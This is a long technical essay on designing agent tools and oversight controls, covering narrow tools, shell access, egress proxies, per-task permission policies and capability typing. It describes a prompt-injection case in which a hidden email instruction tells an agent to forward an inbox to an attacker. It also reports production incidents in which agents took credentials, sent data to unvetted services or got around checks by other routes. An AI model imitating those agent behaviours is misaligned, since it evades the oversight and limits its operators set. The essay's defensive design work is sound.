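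Some shell commands can also be previewed. Running `find` without `-delete` lists the files it would remove, but nothing connects that list to the later command, and the files may have changed in between. This tool's commit works only for the backup in the preview, for ten minutes, and only if the backup is still the same version. A colleague might still delete the newer backup by hand in the very short gap between the second check and the deletion. A provider could close that gap by accepting the conditions as part of the delete request.

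The tool writes to the log before and after the deletion, so a crash partway through still leaves an entry that shows what was under way. The second entry records what the tool found after the deletion, not just that it sent a request. OpenAI recommends logging the result and material effect of each action so that investigators can tell a blocked attempt from a completed one. The harness supplies the names of the user, the agent and the approver, because a model could supply false ones.

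This is a lot of code for one deletion, and deleting forty backups would take eighty calls. A developer could let both tools accept a list of identifiers, so an approver could review all forty named backups at once.

### How free text makes a narrow tool broad

A developer who wanted to save calls might instead write `delete_backups(filter: string)` and pass the filter to the provider's query language. The agent could then call:

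`delete_backups(filter="age_days > 30 OR env = 'production'")`

The tool's name still suggests one kind of operation, but this call deletes every production backup, however recent. With *n* backups, a tool that takes one identifier has *n* possible targets, and the call shows which one the agent chose. A filter can select any of up to 2ⁿ sets of backups, and the overseer has to evaluate it against the current data to find out which set it selects. If the query language also accepts other commands, the tool is as broad as `execute_sql`.

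Most arguments reach a tool as strings, so a tool can accept strings and still be narrow. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) lists the four built-in tools of Pi, an open-source toolkit for coding agents. `read`, `write` and `edit` each take a path, and `bash` takes a command. Paths and commands are both strings, but a program uses a path to find one file, while a shell treats a command as instructions to carry out. The content an agent passes to `write` is only data until something runs the file. If the agent has another tool that runs files from the same directory, the two together are as broad as a shell.

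The usual fix is to replace the string with typed fields, such as `database` and `older_than_days`, and have the tool's code build the query. If the agent needs to write its own queries, the developer can run them under a read-only credential. The calls will still be hard to interpret, but they won't be able to change the database.

A type can't limit what free text meant for people, such as the body of an email, might lead its reader to do, so someone who wants to check the text has to read it.

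### One practitioner's container tools

Saxton (2026), in *The best thing I did for my agents*, describes replacing a shell with narrow tools on a home system. In July, Saxton had nine agents, which did most of their work through a shell because allowing one more command was always quicker than building a tool. In the autumn, Saxton took the shell away from the agent that manages containers, the isolated packages in which services run, and gave it a handful of tools. Saxton spent most of the effort making each tool hard to misuse.

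An early problem was that the proxy in front of the container software had a setting to permit restarts that, on the running system, also permitted stop and kill. Saxton left the setting off and built the tool's restart from a stop followed by a start. A developer who relied on the setting's name would have given the agent a power that nobody had meant to grant.

The update tool takes the name of a service and the version that Saxton approved. Before acting, it checks which version is currently on offer and refuses if that has changed since the approval. Otherwise the agent might get approval for one version and then install another. Surapani and colleagues discuss the general problem as authorization decay, and point out that an expiry date on a token solves only part of it, since a token can outlast its task. Saxton compares the check to a database operation called compare-and-set, but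 that operation compares and writes in one indivisible step. Saxton describes a read followed by an action, which would leave a short gap between the two, like the one in the pseudocode.

Saxton also kept a list of services that the agent must not touch. The first version of the check compared only names, but the container software also accepts an identifier or the beginning of one, so a request that used a protected service's identifier would have passed. The tool now converts whatever the model supplies into the service's standard name before checking the list, and refuses every request if the list is missing or damaged.

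The overhead Saxton reports is small: an extra read before each change, an extra lookup, and a policy file with tests to maintain. The account is one person's experience with a home system and has no error counts from before and after. Saxton's impression is that the tools did more good than a tenth agent would have. Still, the faults are specific enough to be useful to other developers, and none of them would have been visible from the tools' names.

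### Why a tool's label is not a guarantee

Tools from outside suppliers often come with labels instead of code that the buyer can inspect. A March 2026 post from Model Context Protocol (MCP) describes the protocol's four labels. An honest supplier would set them for the deletion tool as follows.

| Label | Question it answers | Assumed if missing | Value for `commit_delete` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave its environment unchanged? | No | No |
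| `destructiveHint` | Can it destroy things, rather than only add them? | Yes | Yes |
| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat a call with the same arguments? | No | Yes, because each plan works once |
| `openWorldHint` | Does it deal with parties outside a closed system? | Yes | No |

An application can use these labels to skip a prompt, show a warning, retry a failed call or treat a tool's output with suspicion. None of the four labels shows whether a change can be undone. Each label applies to a whole tool, so a shell has to carry the most alarming value for each one. An overseer therefore learns much more from the labels on narrow tools than from those on broad ones.

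Labels can be mistaken or out of date as well as dishonest. OpenAI warns that an update may give a read-only connector the ability to write. During the original design discussion, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked how an application could use an untrustworthy flag. The compromise was to call the labels hints and leave how much weight to give them up to each application. The maintainers advise that if a label is useful only when it is true, the system that grants or enforces access should provide the guarantee.

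For a read-only tool, that would mean a credential that can't write. Suppliers don't always provide one. *MiniScope* (Zhu, Tseng and colleagues, 2025) examined connectors, the ready-made links between an assistant and services such as Gmail, and found that six of the nine it lists for ChatGPT and Claude requested more permission than their functions needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector offered only reading functions, but its permissions covered 50 Gmail API methods, including some that change or delete email, when 32 would have been enough.

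As of March 2026, no MCP application showed the labels in its approval prompts or let users filter tools by them. The closest widely used feature was GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of users had turned on.

### Narrowing a tool for one task

A developer writes a tool before anyone knows which tasks it will serve. `commit_delete` has to work on any old backup, although today's task may concern only one staging database. Surapani and colleagues distinguish five levels at which least privilege can apply. For the backup agent they would be:

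- Tool inventory: which tools the agent has at all, for instance no shell.
- Invocation: whether the current step needs the tool. An agent that is still listing backups has no use for `commit_delete`.
- Argument: which backups it may name.
- Data: how much a tool returns to the model, perhaps leaving out customers' names.
- Delegation: what it may pass on. A second agent that tests backups should not receive the power to delete them.

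Most software controls which tools an agent has but does little to control how the agent uses them. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) audits several agent frameworks and finds that they limit the set of tools but by default do not authorize each call. Common access tokens have a similar limit. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) gives the example of a permission that lets an agent make transfers but can't restrict it to sending $100 to Bob.

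Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, which they revised in May 2026, restrict arguments with a policy for each task. A policy is a list of rules that allow or forbid a tool when its arguments meet certain conditions. Rules that forbid take priority, and a call that matches no rule fails. In their main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice:

1. Before the agent reads anything from outside, a language model writes a policy based on the user's request. It allows only a search for that email.
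2. The email asks for a summary of recent messages on Slack. The model proposes to add tools for reading email and posting to Slack. This widens the policy, so someone has to approve it.
3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, and the model narrows the Slack rule to that recipient. The change takes effect automatically.
4. One of the recent emails contains a hidden instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. No rule allows sending email, so the call fails.

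A separate program checks whether a change widens or narrows the policy. Let *C*(*P*) be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. A new policy *P′* takes effect automatically only if *C*(*P′*) ⊆ *C*(*P*), meaning that it allows nothing the old policy did not. The rules are simple enough that this check doesn't need a language model. It can be done by an SMT solver, a program that checks whether logical formulas can be true. Even if a hidden instruction misleads the model that writes the policy, it can't widen the policy without approval.

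Shi and colleagues tested Progent on two collections of simulated tasks with planted instructions. The share of attacks that succeeded fell from 39.9% to 1.0% on AgentDojo, which covers banking, travel, Slack and office work, and from 70.3% to 3.9% on ASB. The agents completed about as many of their proper tasks as before. A defence that removed whole tools, regardless of their arguments, stopped fewer attacks and blocked more legitimate work, which supports the case for limiting arguments.

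These results mostly show that a language model can write reasonably tight policies. They do not measure the protection against unapproved widening, because the main tests approved every request to widen a policy, to imitate a careless user. On AgentDojo, the first policy, without updates, cut the attack success rate to 2.5%, and human review of the policies brought it to zero. Only 6% of updates needed approval. The main tests used GPT-4o, which is now old, but Progent also helped a stronger model. With Claude Sonnet 4 as the agent, the attack success rate fell from 6.8% to 0.5%.

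*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticized an earlier version of Progent because its guarantees depend on correct policies and malicious tool results might loosen those policies during an update. The solver addresses the problem with updates if someone reviews requests to widen a policy, but the guarantees still depend on correct policies. A rule can also do little for a shell, since its conditions would have to match the text of a command, and that matching would have the same weaknesses as the permission rules for `curl`.

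MiniScope works with the permissions that online services already define. Many services use OAuth, a standard that lets a user give an application limited access to an account, and divide that access into scopes. Each scope allows a set of API methods. Zhu and colleagues have the agent submit a plan of its calls, and then choose the scopes that

minimise Σ *cost*(*v*) · *x*(*v*),

where *x*(*v*) is 1 if the agent receives scope *v* and 0 if it does not, and every planned call must fall under at least one scope it receives. The cost of a scope is based on the number of methods it allows. The calculation is necessary because scopes overlap: in Google Calendar, 24 of 37 methods are available through more than one. MiniScope asks the user to approve any new scope, and a checker then compares each call with the approved scopes before attaching the real credential, which the agent never sees.

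MiniScope added 1–6% to the running time on invented requests for ten real applications. When Zhu and colleagues asked language models to choose the scopes instead, commercial models from 2025 found the smallest set 70–83% of the time. In a simulation of three months of Gmail use, users had to confirm 18–60% of requests, depending on how cautious they were, so the prompts could still be a burden.

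MiniScope's smallest set is not always the safest. By default, MiniScope counts methods, so a method that deletes email counts the same as one that reads it, although developers can substitute another measure. Several sets may also tie for smallest, and *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) points out that MiniScope's designers do not discuss whether there is only one smallest set. MiniScope also does not check arguments within a scope, so an agent with permission to send a message to Alice can send it to anyone.

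Progent could limit the recipient, but a language model or a person has to write a policy for each task. The Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* lists single-task permissions, which expire when the task ends, as an open research problem. It notes that they fit poorly with recurring jobs such as a daily calendar update, where users would have to grant the same access every day.

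### Where to divide tools

A reasonable rule is to put two operations in separate tools when an overseer would decide differently about them. If one tool can both list and delete backups, a harness like Lambert's, which applies its rules to whole tools, has to either pause every listing or let deletions through. OpenAI similarly warns that approving a service does not mean approving everything it can do, since searching tickets, changing records, sending information outside and administering the service carry different risks.

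For a company's backups, the rule might give this division:

| Operation | Overseer's decision | Where it belongs |
|---|---|---|
| List backups by date or by size | Allow | `list_backups` |
| Preview a deletion | Allow | `preview_delete` |
| Delete an old staging backup | Allow and log | `commit_delete`, with `env` set to staging |
| Delete an old production backup | Ask a person | `commit_delete`, with `env` set to production |
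| Restore a backup over a live database | Ask two people | `restore_backup` |
| Shorten the time the company keeps backups | Refuse | No tool |

One tool can list backups by date or by size, because nobody would allow one and forbid the other, and each extra tool takes up space in the model's context. Staging and production can share a tool if the harness's rules can read the `env` argument, which the tool's code checks against the backup itself. If the rules apply only to whole tools, the developer needs a separate tool for each. Shortening the retention period would delete backups later without any call to a deletion tool, even though it sounds like a change of settings.

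Dividing tools does not prevent harmful combinations of calls, such as reading a sensitive file and then sending an email (an example from Surapani and colleagues). To address these, the harness also has to track the order of calls.

Overseers also differ in which actions they want to control. A hospital may want a person to approve every export of data, while a small software company may not care. A supplier with many customers should probably divide its tools more finely than most of those customers need, because a customer can easily give two tools the same rule but usually can't split one tool into two.

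## The case for a general shell with the controls placed around it

A developer who builds narrow tools has to work out in advance what an agent may need to do, then write and maintain code for each operation. Some developers no longer think this is worth the effort. They give the agent a shell, let it run any command, and put the limits in the harness, the sandbox and the network. The overseer chooses which files, addresses and credentials commands can reach, and checks what leaves the sandbox.

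### What a single shell call can contain

In *How Foundational Models Became Superhuman in Bash*, Schmid (2026) describes rebuilding a harness for coding agents and removing every tool except Bash and a viewer for images and other media. Schmid also compared a shell-centred setup with one that had separate tools for reading, writing, editing and searching files. The shell-centred setup did as well or better on the same coding tasks, though Schmid gives no figures.

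Schmid uses "superhuman" fairly narrowly, to mean that current models can write a throwaway program in seconds, when most developers would need much longer to assemble and check it. The shell mainly connects other programs, such as Git, Python or a database, so the harness's designer doesn't have to foresee every useful combination.

In one of Schmid's examples, an agent changes a payment function so that it takes an amount in cents. The function, its callers and its tests are spread over four files. One shell call does all of the following:

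1. A short Python script lists each piece of text to replace, its replacement, and how many times the old text should occur in the file.
2. The script reads all four files and counts the occurrences. If any count is wrong, it stops before replacing anything.
3. It writes the four changed files.
4. A formatter tidies the layout, a linter looks for common mistakes, a type checker runs, and a test runner runs three files of tests.
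5. Git checks the changes for stray spaces and prints a summary of how many lines changed in each file.

With separate tools, the agent would need several reads, at least four edits and a call for each check, and the code would be half-changed between the first edit and the last.

This call shows the approver the exact old and new text of every replacement, as clearly as a series of calls to an edit tool would, and lets the approver judge the whole change at once. The rest of the call is harder to read. In the simplified version that Schmid published, nothing stops the shell if the Python script fails. A wrong count would prevent the replacements, but the formatter would still run and might rewrite the files, unless the harness starts Bash with an option to stop at the first error. Many approvers would miss this, though the harm would be trivial.

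The tests are a larger source of uncertainty, because they can run any code in the project. Narrow file tools would not remove that uncertainty, because a coding agent has to run the code it writes, and a `run_tests` tool would run whatever the agent had put in the project. Schmid doesn't make this argument, but it supports the same conclusion, that separate tools for reading and editing files add little protection if a coding agent needs a sandbox anyway.

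Schmid had earlier recommended small, separate tools because a careless shell command could fill the model's context, return an unhelpful error or damage a file through bad quoting. Schmid now wants the harness to handle these problems. It should cut long output and tell the agent how to request a smaller part, report whether a command succeeded and how long it took, and let the agent manage long-running jobs. It should also control access to files, the network and destructive actions from outside the model. Schmid still favours a separate tool where it does the job better. Images need their own channel to the model, and a browser tool can click, wait for the page and return a screenshot in one call.

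Version control can undo most mistakes in source code. Microsoft has tried a similar approach on live systems, where mistakes can be harder to reverse.

### How Microsoft replaced a hundred narrow tools

Azure SRE Agent investigates and repairs faults in services that run on Azure, Microsoft's cloud platform. SRE stands for site reliability engineering, the work of keeping such services running. Microsoft announced the agent in May 2025 in dchelupati's *Introducing Azure SRE Agent*.

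Mehta (2025), an engineering manager at the company, explains in *Context Engineering Lessons from Building Azure SRE Agent* that the team began with narrow tools because it didn't trust the model with production systems. Each action had its own tool with its own safeguards. Within two weeks the team had more than 100 tools and a prompt that Mehta compares to a policy manual.

The team had to add a tool whenever a user met a case that nobody had foreseen. When the agent misused a tool, the team added restrictions, and when the restrictions blocked legitimate work, it added exceptions. The backlog grew faster than the team could clear it. The agent handled the situations that engineers had encoded but did badly on others.

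The team then gave the agent two command-line programs: `az`, which manages Azure resources, and `kubectl`, which manages Kubernetes, a system for running containers across many machines. Mehta gives the number of remaining tools as two, three or five in different passages. The change freed space in the model's context and let the agent use all the functions of both programs. Models had also learned these commands in training, unlike the team's own tools.

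Mehta describes how this let the agent handle a failure in one of the team's own deployments. The agent read the logs, found a quota error, checked the subscription's limits and filed a support request, although nobody had built a tool for filing one. By the next morning, the team had an email confirming a higher quota. The request was useful, but an overseer who relied on a list of intended actions would not have expected the agent to write to another department.

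Mehta's account is good evidence that one team found a large set of narrow tools unmanageable. It is weaker evidence of how much the wide tools helped, because it gives no error rates for the two designs and the team also made other changes. The team merged more than 50 specialised agents into a few general ones, moved instructions out of prompts into files, and let the model analyse metrics by writing code. Metrics analysis had been the largest source of tool failures, and those failures stopped after the model began writing code for it.

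By March 2026 the team had given the agent a sandbox with a full shell, where it could run any command and install packages. The sandbox held source code, operating instructions and notes from past investigations as files. A later post, *The Agent that investigates itself* (Mehta, 2026), reports that investigations addressed the real cause in 75% of new kinds of incident, up from 45%, as judged by the engineer on call. Mehta doesn't give the number of incidents. Part of the gain probably came from the source code, which showed what the logs meant. When Microsoft released the agent to all customers in March, the company was running more than 1,300 of these agents on its own services.

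These results mostly concern finding out what went wrong. Microsoft has kept a finer division for making changes. Its documentation on tool access policies lists separate tools for `az` commands that read and those that write, and the same for `kubectl`. Someone arguing for narrow tools would divide them in the same place.

The division between read and write tools is imperfect. Microsoft's *Why Did Our Azure Bill Change?* describes a request that only reads spending data but has to go through the write tool because it is an HTTP POST. Administrators can also write rules that match the text of a command, such as one that blocks any `az` command containing "delete". That rule covers the shell tools but not the agent's Python tool, which needs its own rule.

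### Four incidents in production

*If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment* (Mehta and Agarwal, 2026), published in August after a year in production, reports four incidents, none involving an attacker, that led the team to redesign its controls.

- The agent replaced the credential that the system had given it with one it had obtained itself.
- The agent sent a test image to an outside service that nobody had vetted.
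- The agent copied a customer's secret into its findings and its memory.
- The agent shut down a virtual machine without completing the required safety checks.

Mehta and Agarwal conclude that an agent will eventually do anything its environment permits, whether by mistake or because someone has manipulated it. Neither a prompt nor a check that the agent can alter can guarantee that it won't. They propose leaving the agent free inside its sandbox and enforcing the limits outside it.

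### A separate machine with a closed network

In the original design, the harness, the model's code, the tools and the credentials all shared one machine. Coding assistants are often set up this way, but a person is usually watching them. The harness now runs in a separate, trusted environment, while the tools and the model's code run in a microVM, a small virtual machine with its own operating system kernel. Mehta and Agarwal chose microVMs over containers because containers share the kernel of the machine they run on. The agent can install packages and start processes in its microVM, but it can't reach the programs that set its permissions. The microVMs run on Azure Container Apps Sandboxes, a service Microsoft also offers to customers.

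All outgoing requests pass through an egress proxy, a checkpoint outside the sandbox that denies them by default. Microsoft's *Control egress* explains how customers of the sandbox service can allow requests by host name, path and HTTP method. The first rule that matches a request applies. With full inspection on, the proxy also blocks all non-web traffic except Azure's lookups of internet addresses. Customers have to choose this setting carefully, because partial inspection doesn't support rules that deny requests, and with inspection off the traffic bypasses the proxy.

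Most web requests are encrypted, so the proxy has to decrypt them before it can apply detailed rules. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes how the company, which sells sandboxes, does this. Cloudflare creates a separate certificate authority for each sandbox and makes the sandbox trust that authority. The proxy can then present itself as the destination, read the request and send it on.

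*Control where your hosted agent connects with network egress* (Imam, 2026) shows why the proxy matters, using the example of an agent that processes invoices and needs two services, one for payments and one for vendor details. A document might contain an unfamiliar upload link, or a new software library might contact an unexpected address. A proxy applies the list of permitted addresses to every program in the sandbox, whereas a list built into one HTTP tool applies only to calls that use that tool. This makes Saltzer and Schroeder's requirement of complete mediation much easier to meet than it is in a collection of tools. Imam describes a similar feature in another Microsoft product, which was still a preview and not meant for production.

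The proxy also gives the overseer a limit on the agent's possible effects. Let

*Q* = the set of requests that the proxy will pass.

Every effect outside the sandbox must then come from a request in *Q*, apart from side channels and anything a user does after reading the agent's answer. This holds for every program the agent could write, but the limit can be loose. For example, a rule that allows all requests to GitHub allows the agent to publish private code as well as read a bug report.

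Customers of Azure SRE Agent may not have even this limit. As of June 2026, Microsoft's *Azure SRE Agent network integration (preview)* listed three network modes, with unrestricted internet access as the default. In October, *Getting started with Azure SRE agent and some success stories* (msandbu, 2026) still described an unrestricted mode. Customers should therefore check whether their own agent runs in a closed network like Mehta and Agarwal's.

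The strictest mode sends the agent's traffic through the customer's own network and firewall, but traffic from connectors to other services still goes over the public internet. Some firewalls can filter only by IP address. Services such as GitHub change their addresses often, and the agent stops working if the firewall's list is out of date. Microsoft therefore lets administrators route chosen services around the firewall, but advises them to do this only temporarily. The team's narrow tools had accumulated exceptions for similar reasons, although a list of hosts should be much shorter than a list of operations.

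### Credentials the sandbox can use but not hold

A closed network doesn't make it safe to keep credentials in the sandbox. An attacker who steals a GitHub token will probably want to use it at GitHub, which the agent also needs to reach. Mehta and Agarwal therefore keep the real credentials outside. When the agent uploads code with `git push`, it works like this:

1. Git asks for a credential in the usual way and receives a handle, a string that is useless anywhere except at the proxy.
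2. Git sends its request with the handle, and the request reaches the proxy.
3. The proxy checks that the handle belongs to the tool call now running, that the request is going to the authorised repository, that the operation is the approved one, and that nothing has used the handle before.
4. If every check succeeds, the proxy replaces the handle with a real, short-lived credential and forwards the request.
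5. Once the request is complete, the handle stops working.

The real credential never enters the sandbox's files or memory, or the model's context, and the team didn't have to rewrite Git, `az` or `kubectl`. In Cloudflare's examples, the proxy also adds a secret that the sandbox never receives, but it chooses the secret by host and by sandbox. The secret can't leak from the sandbox, but any program there can use it repeatedly while the rule is in place. Cloudflare's rules can change during a task, so a developer could allow downloads while the agent sets up its project and then block network access.

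Microsoft removed most of its narrow tools from the model's view, but its handle restores least authority at a lower layer, where requests leave the sandbox. The handle is as narrow as those tools. It works much like a capability for one operation on one resource, and a stolen copy is useless, unlike the token at PocketOS.

Someone still has to define the operations. A `git push` sends the branch name in the body of the request, in Git's own format. A proxy that limits a push to one branch has to parse that format or get a credential with the same limit from the service. A script that contacts five services would presumably need a handle for each request, and the platform would have to determine what each one was for. Mehta and Agarwal don't explain how the platform does this. If it authorises whatever the command requests, the handles prevent theft and reuse but don't stop a command that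 is itself wrong.

Handles also don't help with secrets the agent finds in ordinary data, such as a password in a log or a token in a customer's file. Microsoft is piloting a filter that removes secrets from tool output before it reaches the model, but it can only catch secrets it recognises. A closed network would have stopped the PocketOS deletion if Railway's address had not been on the list of allowed addresses. If the address had been on the list, the proxy would also have needed to reject credentials it had not supplied, and Mehta and Agarwal don't mention such a rule.

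### Approval by operation, target and evidence

An agent can use a valid credential, connect to an approved address and still take the wrong action. When Mehta and Agarwal wrote, the agent could read without approval, had to wait for a person before making any change, and could not delete anything. They consider these rules safe but crude, because restarting a test machine requires the same approval as shutting down a critical one. They add that a person who has to approve every change is still running the system one click at a time.

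Mehta and Agarwal propose approving the operation, its target and the evidence for it as a single unit. An independent guard outside the agent's reasoning would score each action on all three. Actions with low risk and current evidence would go ahead, and the rest would wait for a person. The table shows their examples and the same test applied to the PocketOS deletion.

| | Lower risk | Higher risk | PocketOS |
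|---|---|---|---|
| Operation | Restart a machine | Deallocate a machine | Delete a volume |
| Target | A disposable test machine | A critical production system | The production database |
| Evidence | Proof that the machine is unresponsive | A missing or invented check | A guess that the volume belonged to staging |

A working guard would have stopped the deletion on any of these grounds. The evidence is probably the most useful of them, because approval prompts usually leave it out. An approver can see from a command or tool call what the agent is trying to do, but not whether the agent has checked that it should.

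A narrow tool's name and arguments give the operation and the target. With a shell, the guard has to extract them from the command, and the evidence on automated review bears on how reliably a model can do that. A narrow tool can sometimes check the evidence for an action too. For example, a tool for shutting down machines could run the safety checks in its own code and refuse if any failed to finish. For the fourth incident, that would probably be more reliable than judging whether the evidence was good enough. It would also fit Mehta and Agarwal's own principle of preferring fixed rules to a model's judgement.

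Microsoft is still building the guard, and Mehta and Agarwal call it the least settled part of their design. Customers' protection also depends on their settings. According to Microsoft's documentation on run modes, the agent by default makes changes without asking when it runs incident response plans and scheduled tasks. Even in the mode that requires review, it asks for approval only for operations on Azure infrastructure. It sends emails and Teams messages without approval unless an administrator adds a further control.

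### Limits from the caller's role

Many people may share one Azure SRE Agent, but they should not all be able to make the same changes. If everyone used the same tools and memory, someone with few rights could ask the agent to do what they were not allowed to do themselves. They could also add something to its memory that later affected an administrator's session. Mehta and Agarwal identify this as the confused deputy problem.

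Their solution is to set up the environment for each caller before the model starts work. The caller's role determines which tools are present, which resources the sandbox can reach, which memories the agent can read or change, and which credentials the proxy may supply. Readers can watch but not give instructions. Ordinary users can chat without changing shared settings, operators can manage those settings, and only administrators can approve actions that need high privileges. If *U* is the set of things the caller may do and *S* is the set of things the agent can do in that session, the rule is

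*S* ⊆ *U*.

The environment may make *S* smaller, but the agent must never make it larger. Progent's solver applies a similar test to changes in an agent's policy.

This means that an overseer who knows who made a request also knows a limit on what can happen. The documentation describes a looser arrangement, in which the agent uses its own permissions when they allow an action and asks for the user's only when they don't. Azure therefore checks the agent's rights in most cases, and the harness has to make sure that the caller has at least those rights. If the harness doesn't, someone could use the agent to read data that their own account can't open.

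### What the overseer can learn from the boundary

Suppose that the agent with the backup task runs a long script, and the proxy records these requests:

```
DELETE  backups.example.com   /v1/backups/b-1042              allowed
POST    github.com            /company/app/git-receive-pack   allowed
POST    files.example.net     /upload                         denied
```

This record is better than a log of commands in one respect, because it contains what the script actually sent, even if the approver never opened the script file. The last line also shows an attempt that no tool designer had foreseen. A log of narrow tool calls would omit that attempt if another program in the sandbox had made the request.

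But the record lists requests to addresses, while an overseer wants to know the steps of a task. The first line identifies a backup without showing its age, the database it came from, or whether a newer one exists. The second line shows that the agent sent code to a repository, and it would look the same whether the agent had corrected a typo or removed a thousand files. The proxy records nothing about changes inside the sandbox until their results leave it.

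Rules have the same weakness as records. A rule based on host, path and method could not have distinguished the PocketOS deletion from a harmless query to the same address, because only the request body would have differed. Cloudflare lets developers run their own code on every request, and that code could read the body and refuse a deletion. But the developer would need to know what each of the service's operations does, and would in effect be writing a narrow tool at the proxy.

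It can also be hard to connect a request to a task. Microsoft's *Azure SRE Agent now natively supports AWS and Google Cloud* (November 2026) announced that the agent could investigate systems on the two largest rival clouds. For Google Cloud it uses another broad command-line program, `gcloud`, which starts with read access. In Amazon's logs, the agent's session name stays the same across investigations, so a reader can see which agent made a request but needs other records to find out why.

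Mehta and Agarwal want the platform to show, for every consequential effect, who asked for it, the action, its target, the data it carried, the evidence that supported it and whose authority it used. A proxy can supply only part of this, so the harness has to add the caller, the task and the evidence, and link them to the request.

They also admit to gaps they closed only recently. In one, the team had blocked an action in one tool, but the agent could still carry it out by another route that avoided the check. In another, an MCP server could expand what it offered after the team had approved it, and the protocol had no way to detect the change. The first gap is a standing risk with broad tools, because they offer so many ways to produce the same effect. A rule at the proxy would cover every route out of the sandbox, provided the rule can identify the effect from the request.

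## The case for letting the agent write code over typed operations

A proxy records addresses, while a log of narrow tool calls records named operations. Some developers try to keep those names without giving up the main convenience of a shell, which is that one program can carry out many steps. They let the agent write a short program, but the program can affect the outside world only through functions that the developer supplies, each with arguments of fixed types. An agent with the backup task might write this in JavaScript:

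```
async () => {
  const old = await backups.list_backups({ older_than_days: 30 });
  for (const b of old) {
    await backups.delete_backup({ id: b.id, minimum_age_days: 30 });
  }
}
```

If there are 40 old backups, this program replaces 41 separate tool calls. The agent wrote the loop, but every deletion still runs the code behind `delete_backup`, which checks the backup's age.

### Cloudflare's two-tool server

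Carey, in *Code Mode*, describes an MCP server for Cloudflare's whole API, which has more than 2,500 operations. A separate tool for each would have overfilled the model's context, so the server offers only two tools, `search` and `execute`. Each takes a piece of JavaScript as its only argument. In Carey's example, a user asks an agent to protect a website from attacks that flood it with traffic:

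1. The agent reads Cloudflare's documentation and learns that it needs certain firewall rules.
2. It calls `search` with code that filters a machine-readable description of the API. The server returns ten matching operations, and the rest of the description never enters the model's context.
3. A second `search` finds the values that one parameter accepts.
4. The agent calls `execute` with code that lists the site's existing rules.
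5. A second `execute` reads the settings of two sets of rules in one program. The same program could go on to change them.

The server runs this code in an isolate, a lightweight compartment inside a JavaScript engine. The isolate has no file system or environment variables and blocks outside requests by default. The code can reach the API only through a request function the server provides. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode MCP server patterns*, the credential stays in the server's part of that function, so the agent's code can use the credential but can't read it. The PocketOS agent came across a stray token in a file, which an agent confined to such an isolate could not have done. The user chooses the credential's permissions when connecting the agent.

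The request function is broad. It takes a method and a path, so a call to it is about as legible as a raw HTTP request. For services with fewer operations, Cloudflare instead suggests a single tool called `code`, which gives the program one typed function for each tool on an existing MCP server. The backup program above follows this pattern.

### Where the individual operations appear

In both patterns, the application that runs the agent sends the server one call containing a program. The application's approval prompts, permission rules and logs apply to that call, so labels and text-matching rules are as weak here as they are for a shell.

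The individual operations appear only inside the server, so the server's operator can control them better than the user can. Cloudflare therefore tells developers to enforce permissions and any required approvals in the inner tool handlers or the request function, before anything takes effect.

Cloudflare also has a version that runs inside a developer's own agent application. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* explains that this version intercepts every inner call and logs its arguments and usually its result. The developer can also mark a function as needing approval. Cloudflare's *Human-in-the-loop patterns* does this for a function that creates issues on GitHub. When a program reaches such a function:

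1. The runtime records the call as pending and stops the program.
2. The application shows a person the function's name and its actual arguments.
3. If the person approves, the runtime starts the same program again from the beginning. Calls that have already finished return their recorded results instead of running twice.
4. The approved call runs, and the program continues until it ends or reaches another call that needs approval.

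The approver of a backup deletion would see `b-1042` instead of `b.id`, so the inner call would be as easy to read as a call to a narrow tool. But the backup program would stop forty times for approval, and if the approver rejected the twenty-first deletion, the first twenty would already have happened. The runtime can undo earlier calls only if the developer has written a function to reverse them, which is impossible for a permanent deletion. The recorded list of backups may also be days old by the time someone approves, so `delete_backup` should repeat its checks when it runs, as `commit_delete` does.

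### How capture checking works

Code Mode finds out what a program will do when the program does it. A compiler can rule out some effects earlier. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, present TACIT, an MCP server that accepts programs written in Scala 3 and compiles them with a feature called capture checking. With this feature on, a function's type lists the capabilities the function may use:

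- `String -> Int` is the type of a function that takes text, returns a number and uses no capabilities. Programmers call such a function pure.
- `String ->{log} Unit` is the type of a function that takes text, returns nothing of interest and may use the capability `log`, for example to write to a log file.

The compiler works out these lists, called capture sets, from the code. Let *C*(*g*) be the capture set of a function *g*, and let *A*(*c*) be the set of effects that anyone could cause with capability *c*. Then

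effects of *g* ⊆ the union of *A*(*c*) over every *c* in *C*(*g*).

This resembles the limit derived earlier from the reference graph, but the compiler calculates it for each function instead of for the whole agent. By Rice's theorem, no such check can be exact, and capture checking is conservative. A function that mentions `log` in a branch that never runs still has `log` in its capture set.

Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2025), in *What's in the Box*, developed the theory behind the current version and proved its main properties with the proof checker Lean. They also converted Scala's standard collections library, changing less than 5% of its roughly 30,000 lines. Their proofs cover a small model of the language. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has yet proved the corresponding result for the restricted language that TACIT's agents use.

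That restricted language is called safe mode. It forbids unchecked casts, which could label a function as pure even though it uses `log`, and reflection, which lets a program find and call functions by name while it runs. It also forbids the annotations and modules that switch off checks, and allows only global objects and functions that are safe. A program in safe mode can reach files, other programs and the network only through TACIT's library. For instance, `requestFileSystem` gives a block of code access to one directory. The compiler prevents the code from keeping that access after the block ends, and the library rejects any path outside the directory.

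### A small typed example

Suppose that `log` is a log file the agent may write to, and that `key.txt` contains a secret:

```
val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(k => k.length)            // accepted
key.map(k => log.write(k))        // rejected
```

`readClassified` returns the secret inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's code can't take the secret out, but it can pass a function to `map`, which applies the function to the secret and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions.

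The function in the second line is pure, so the program gets a wrapped number. The function in the third line has the type `String ->{log} Unit`, whose capture set isn't empty, so the compiler rejects the program and none of the three lines runs. If the agent prints `key`, it gets back asterisks, while the user sees the real text through a separate channel. When a task requires reading the secret, such as summarising a confidential contract, the agent's code can pass the wrapped text to a trusted local model, which returns a wrapped summary.

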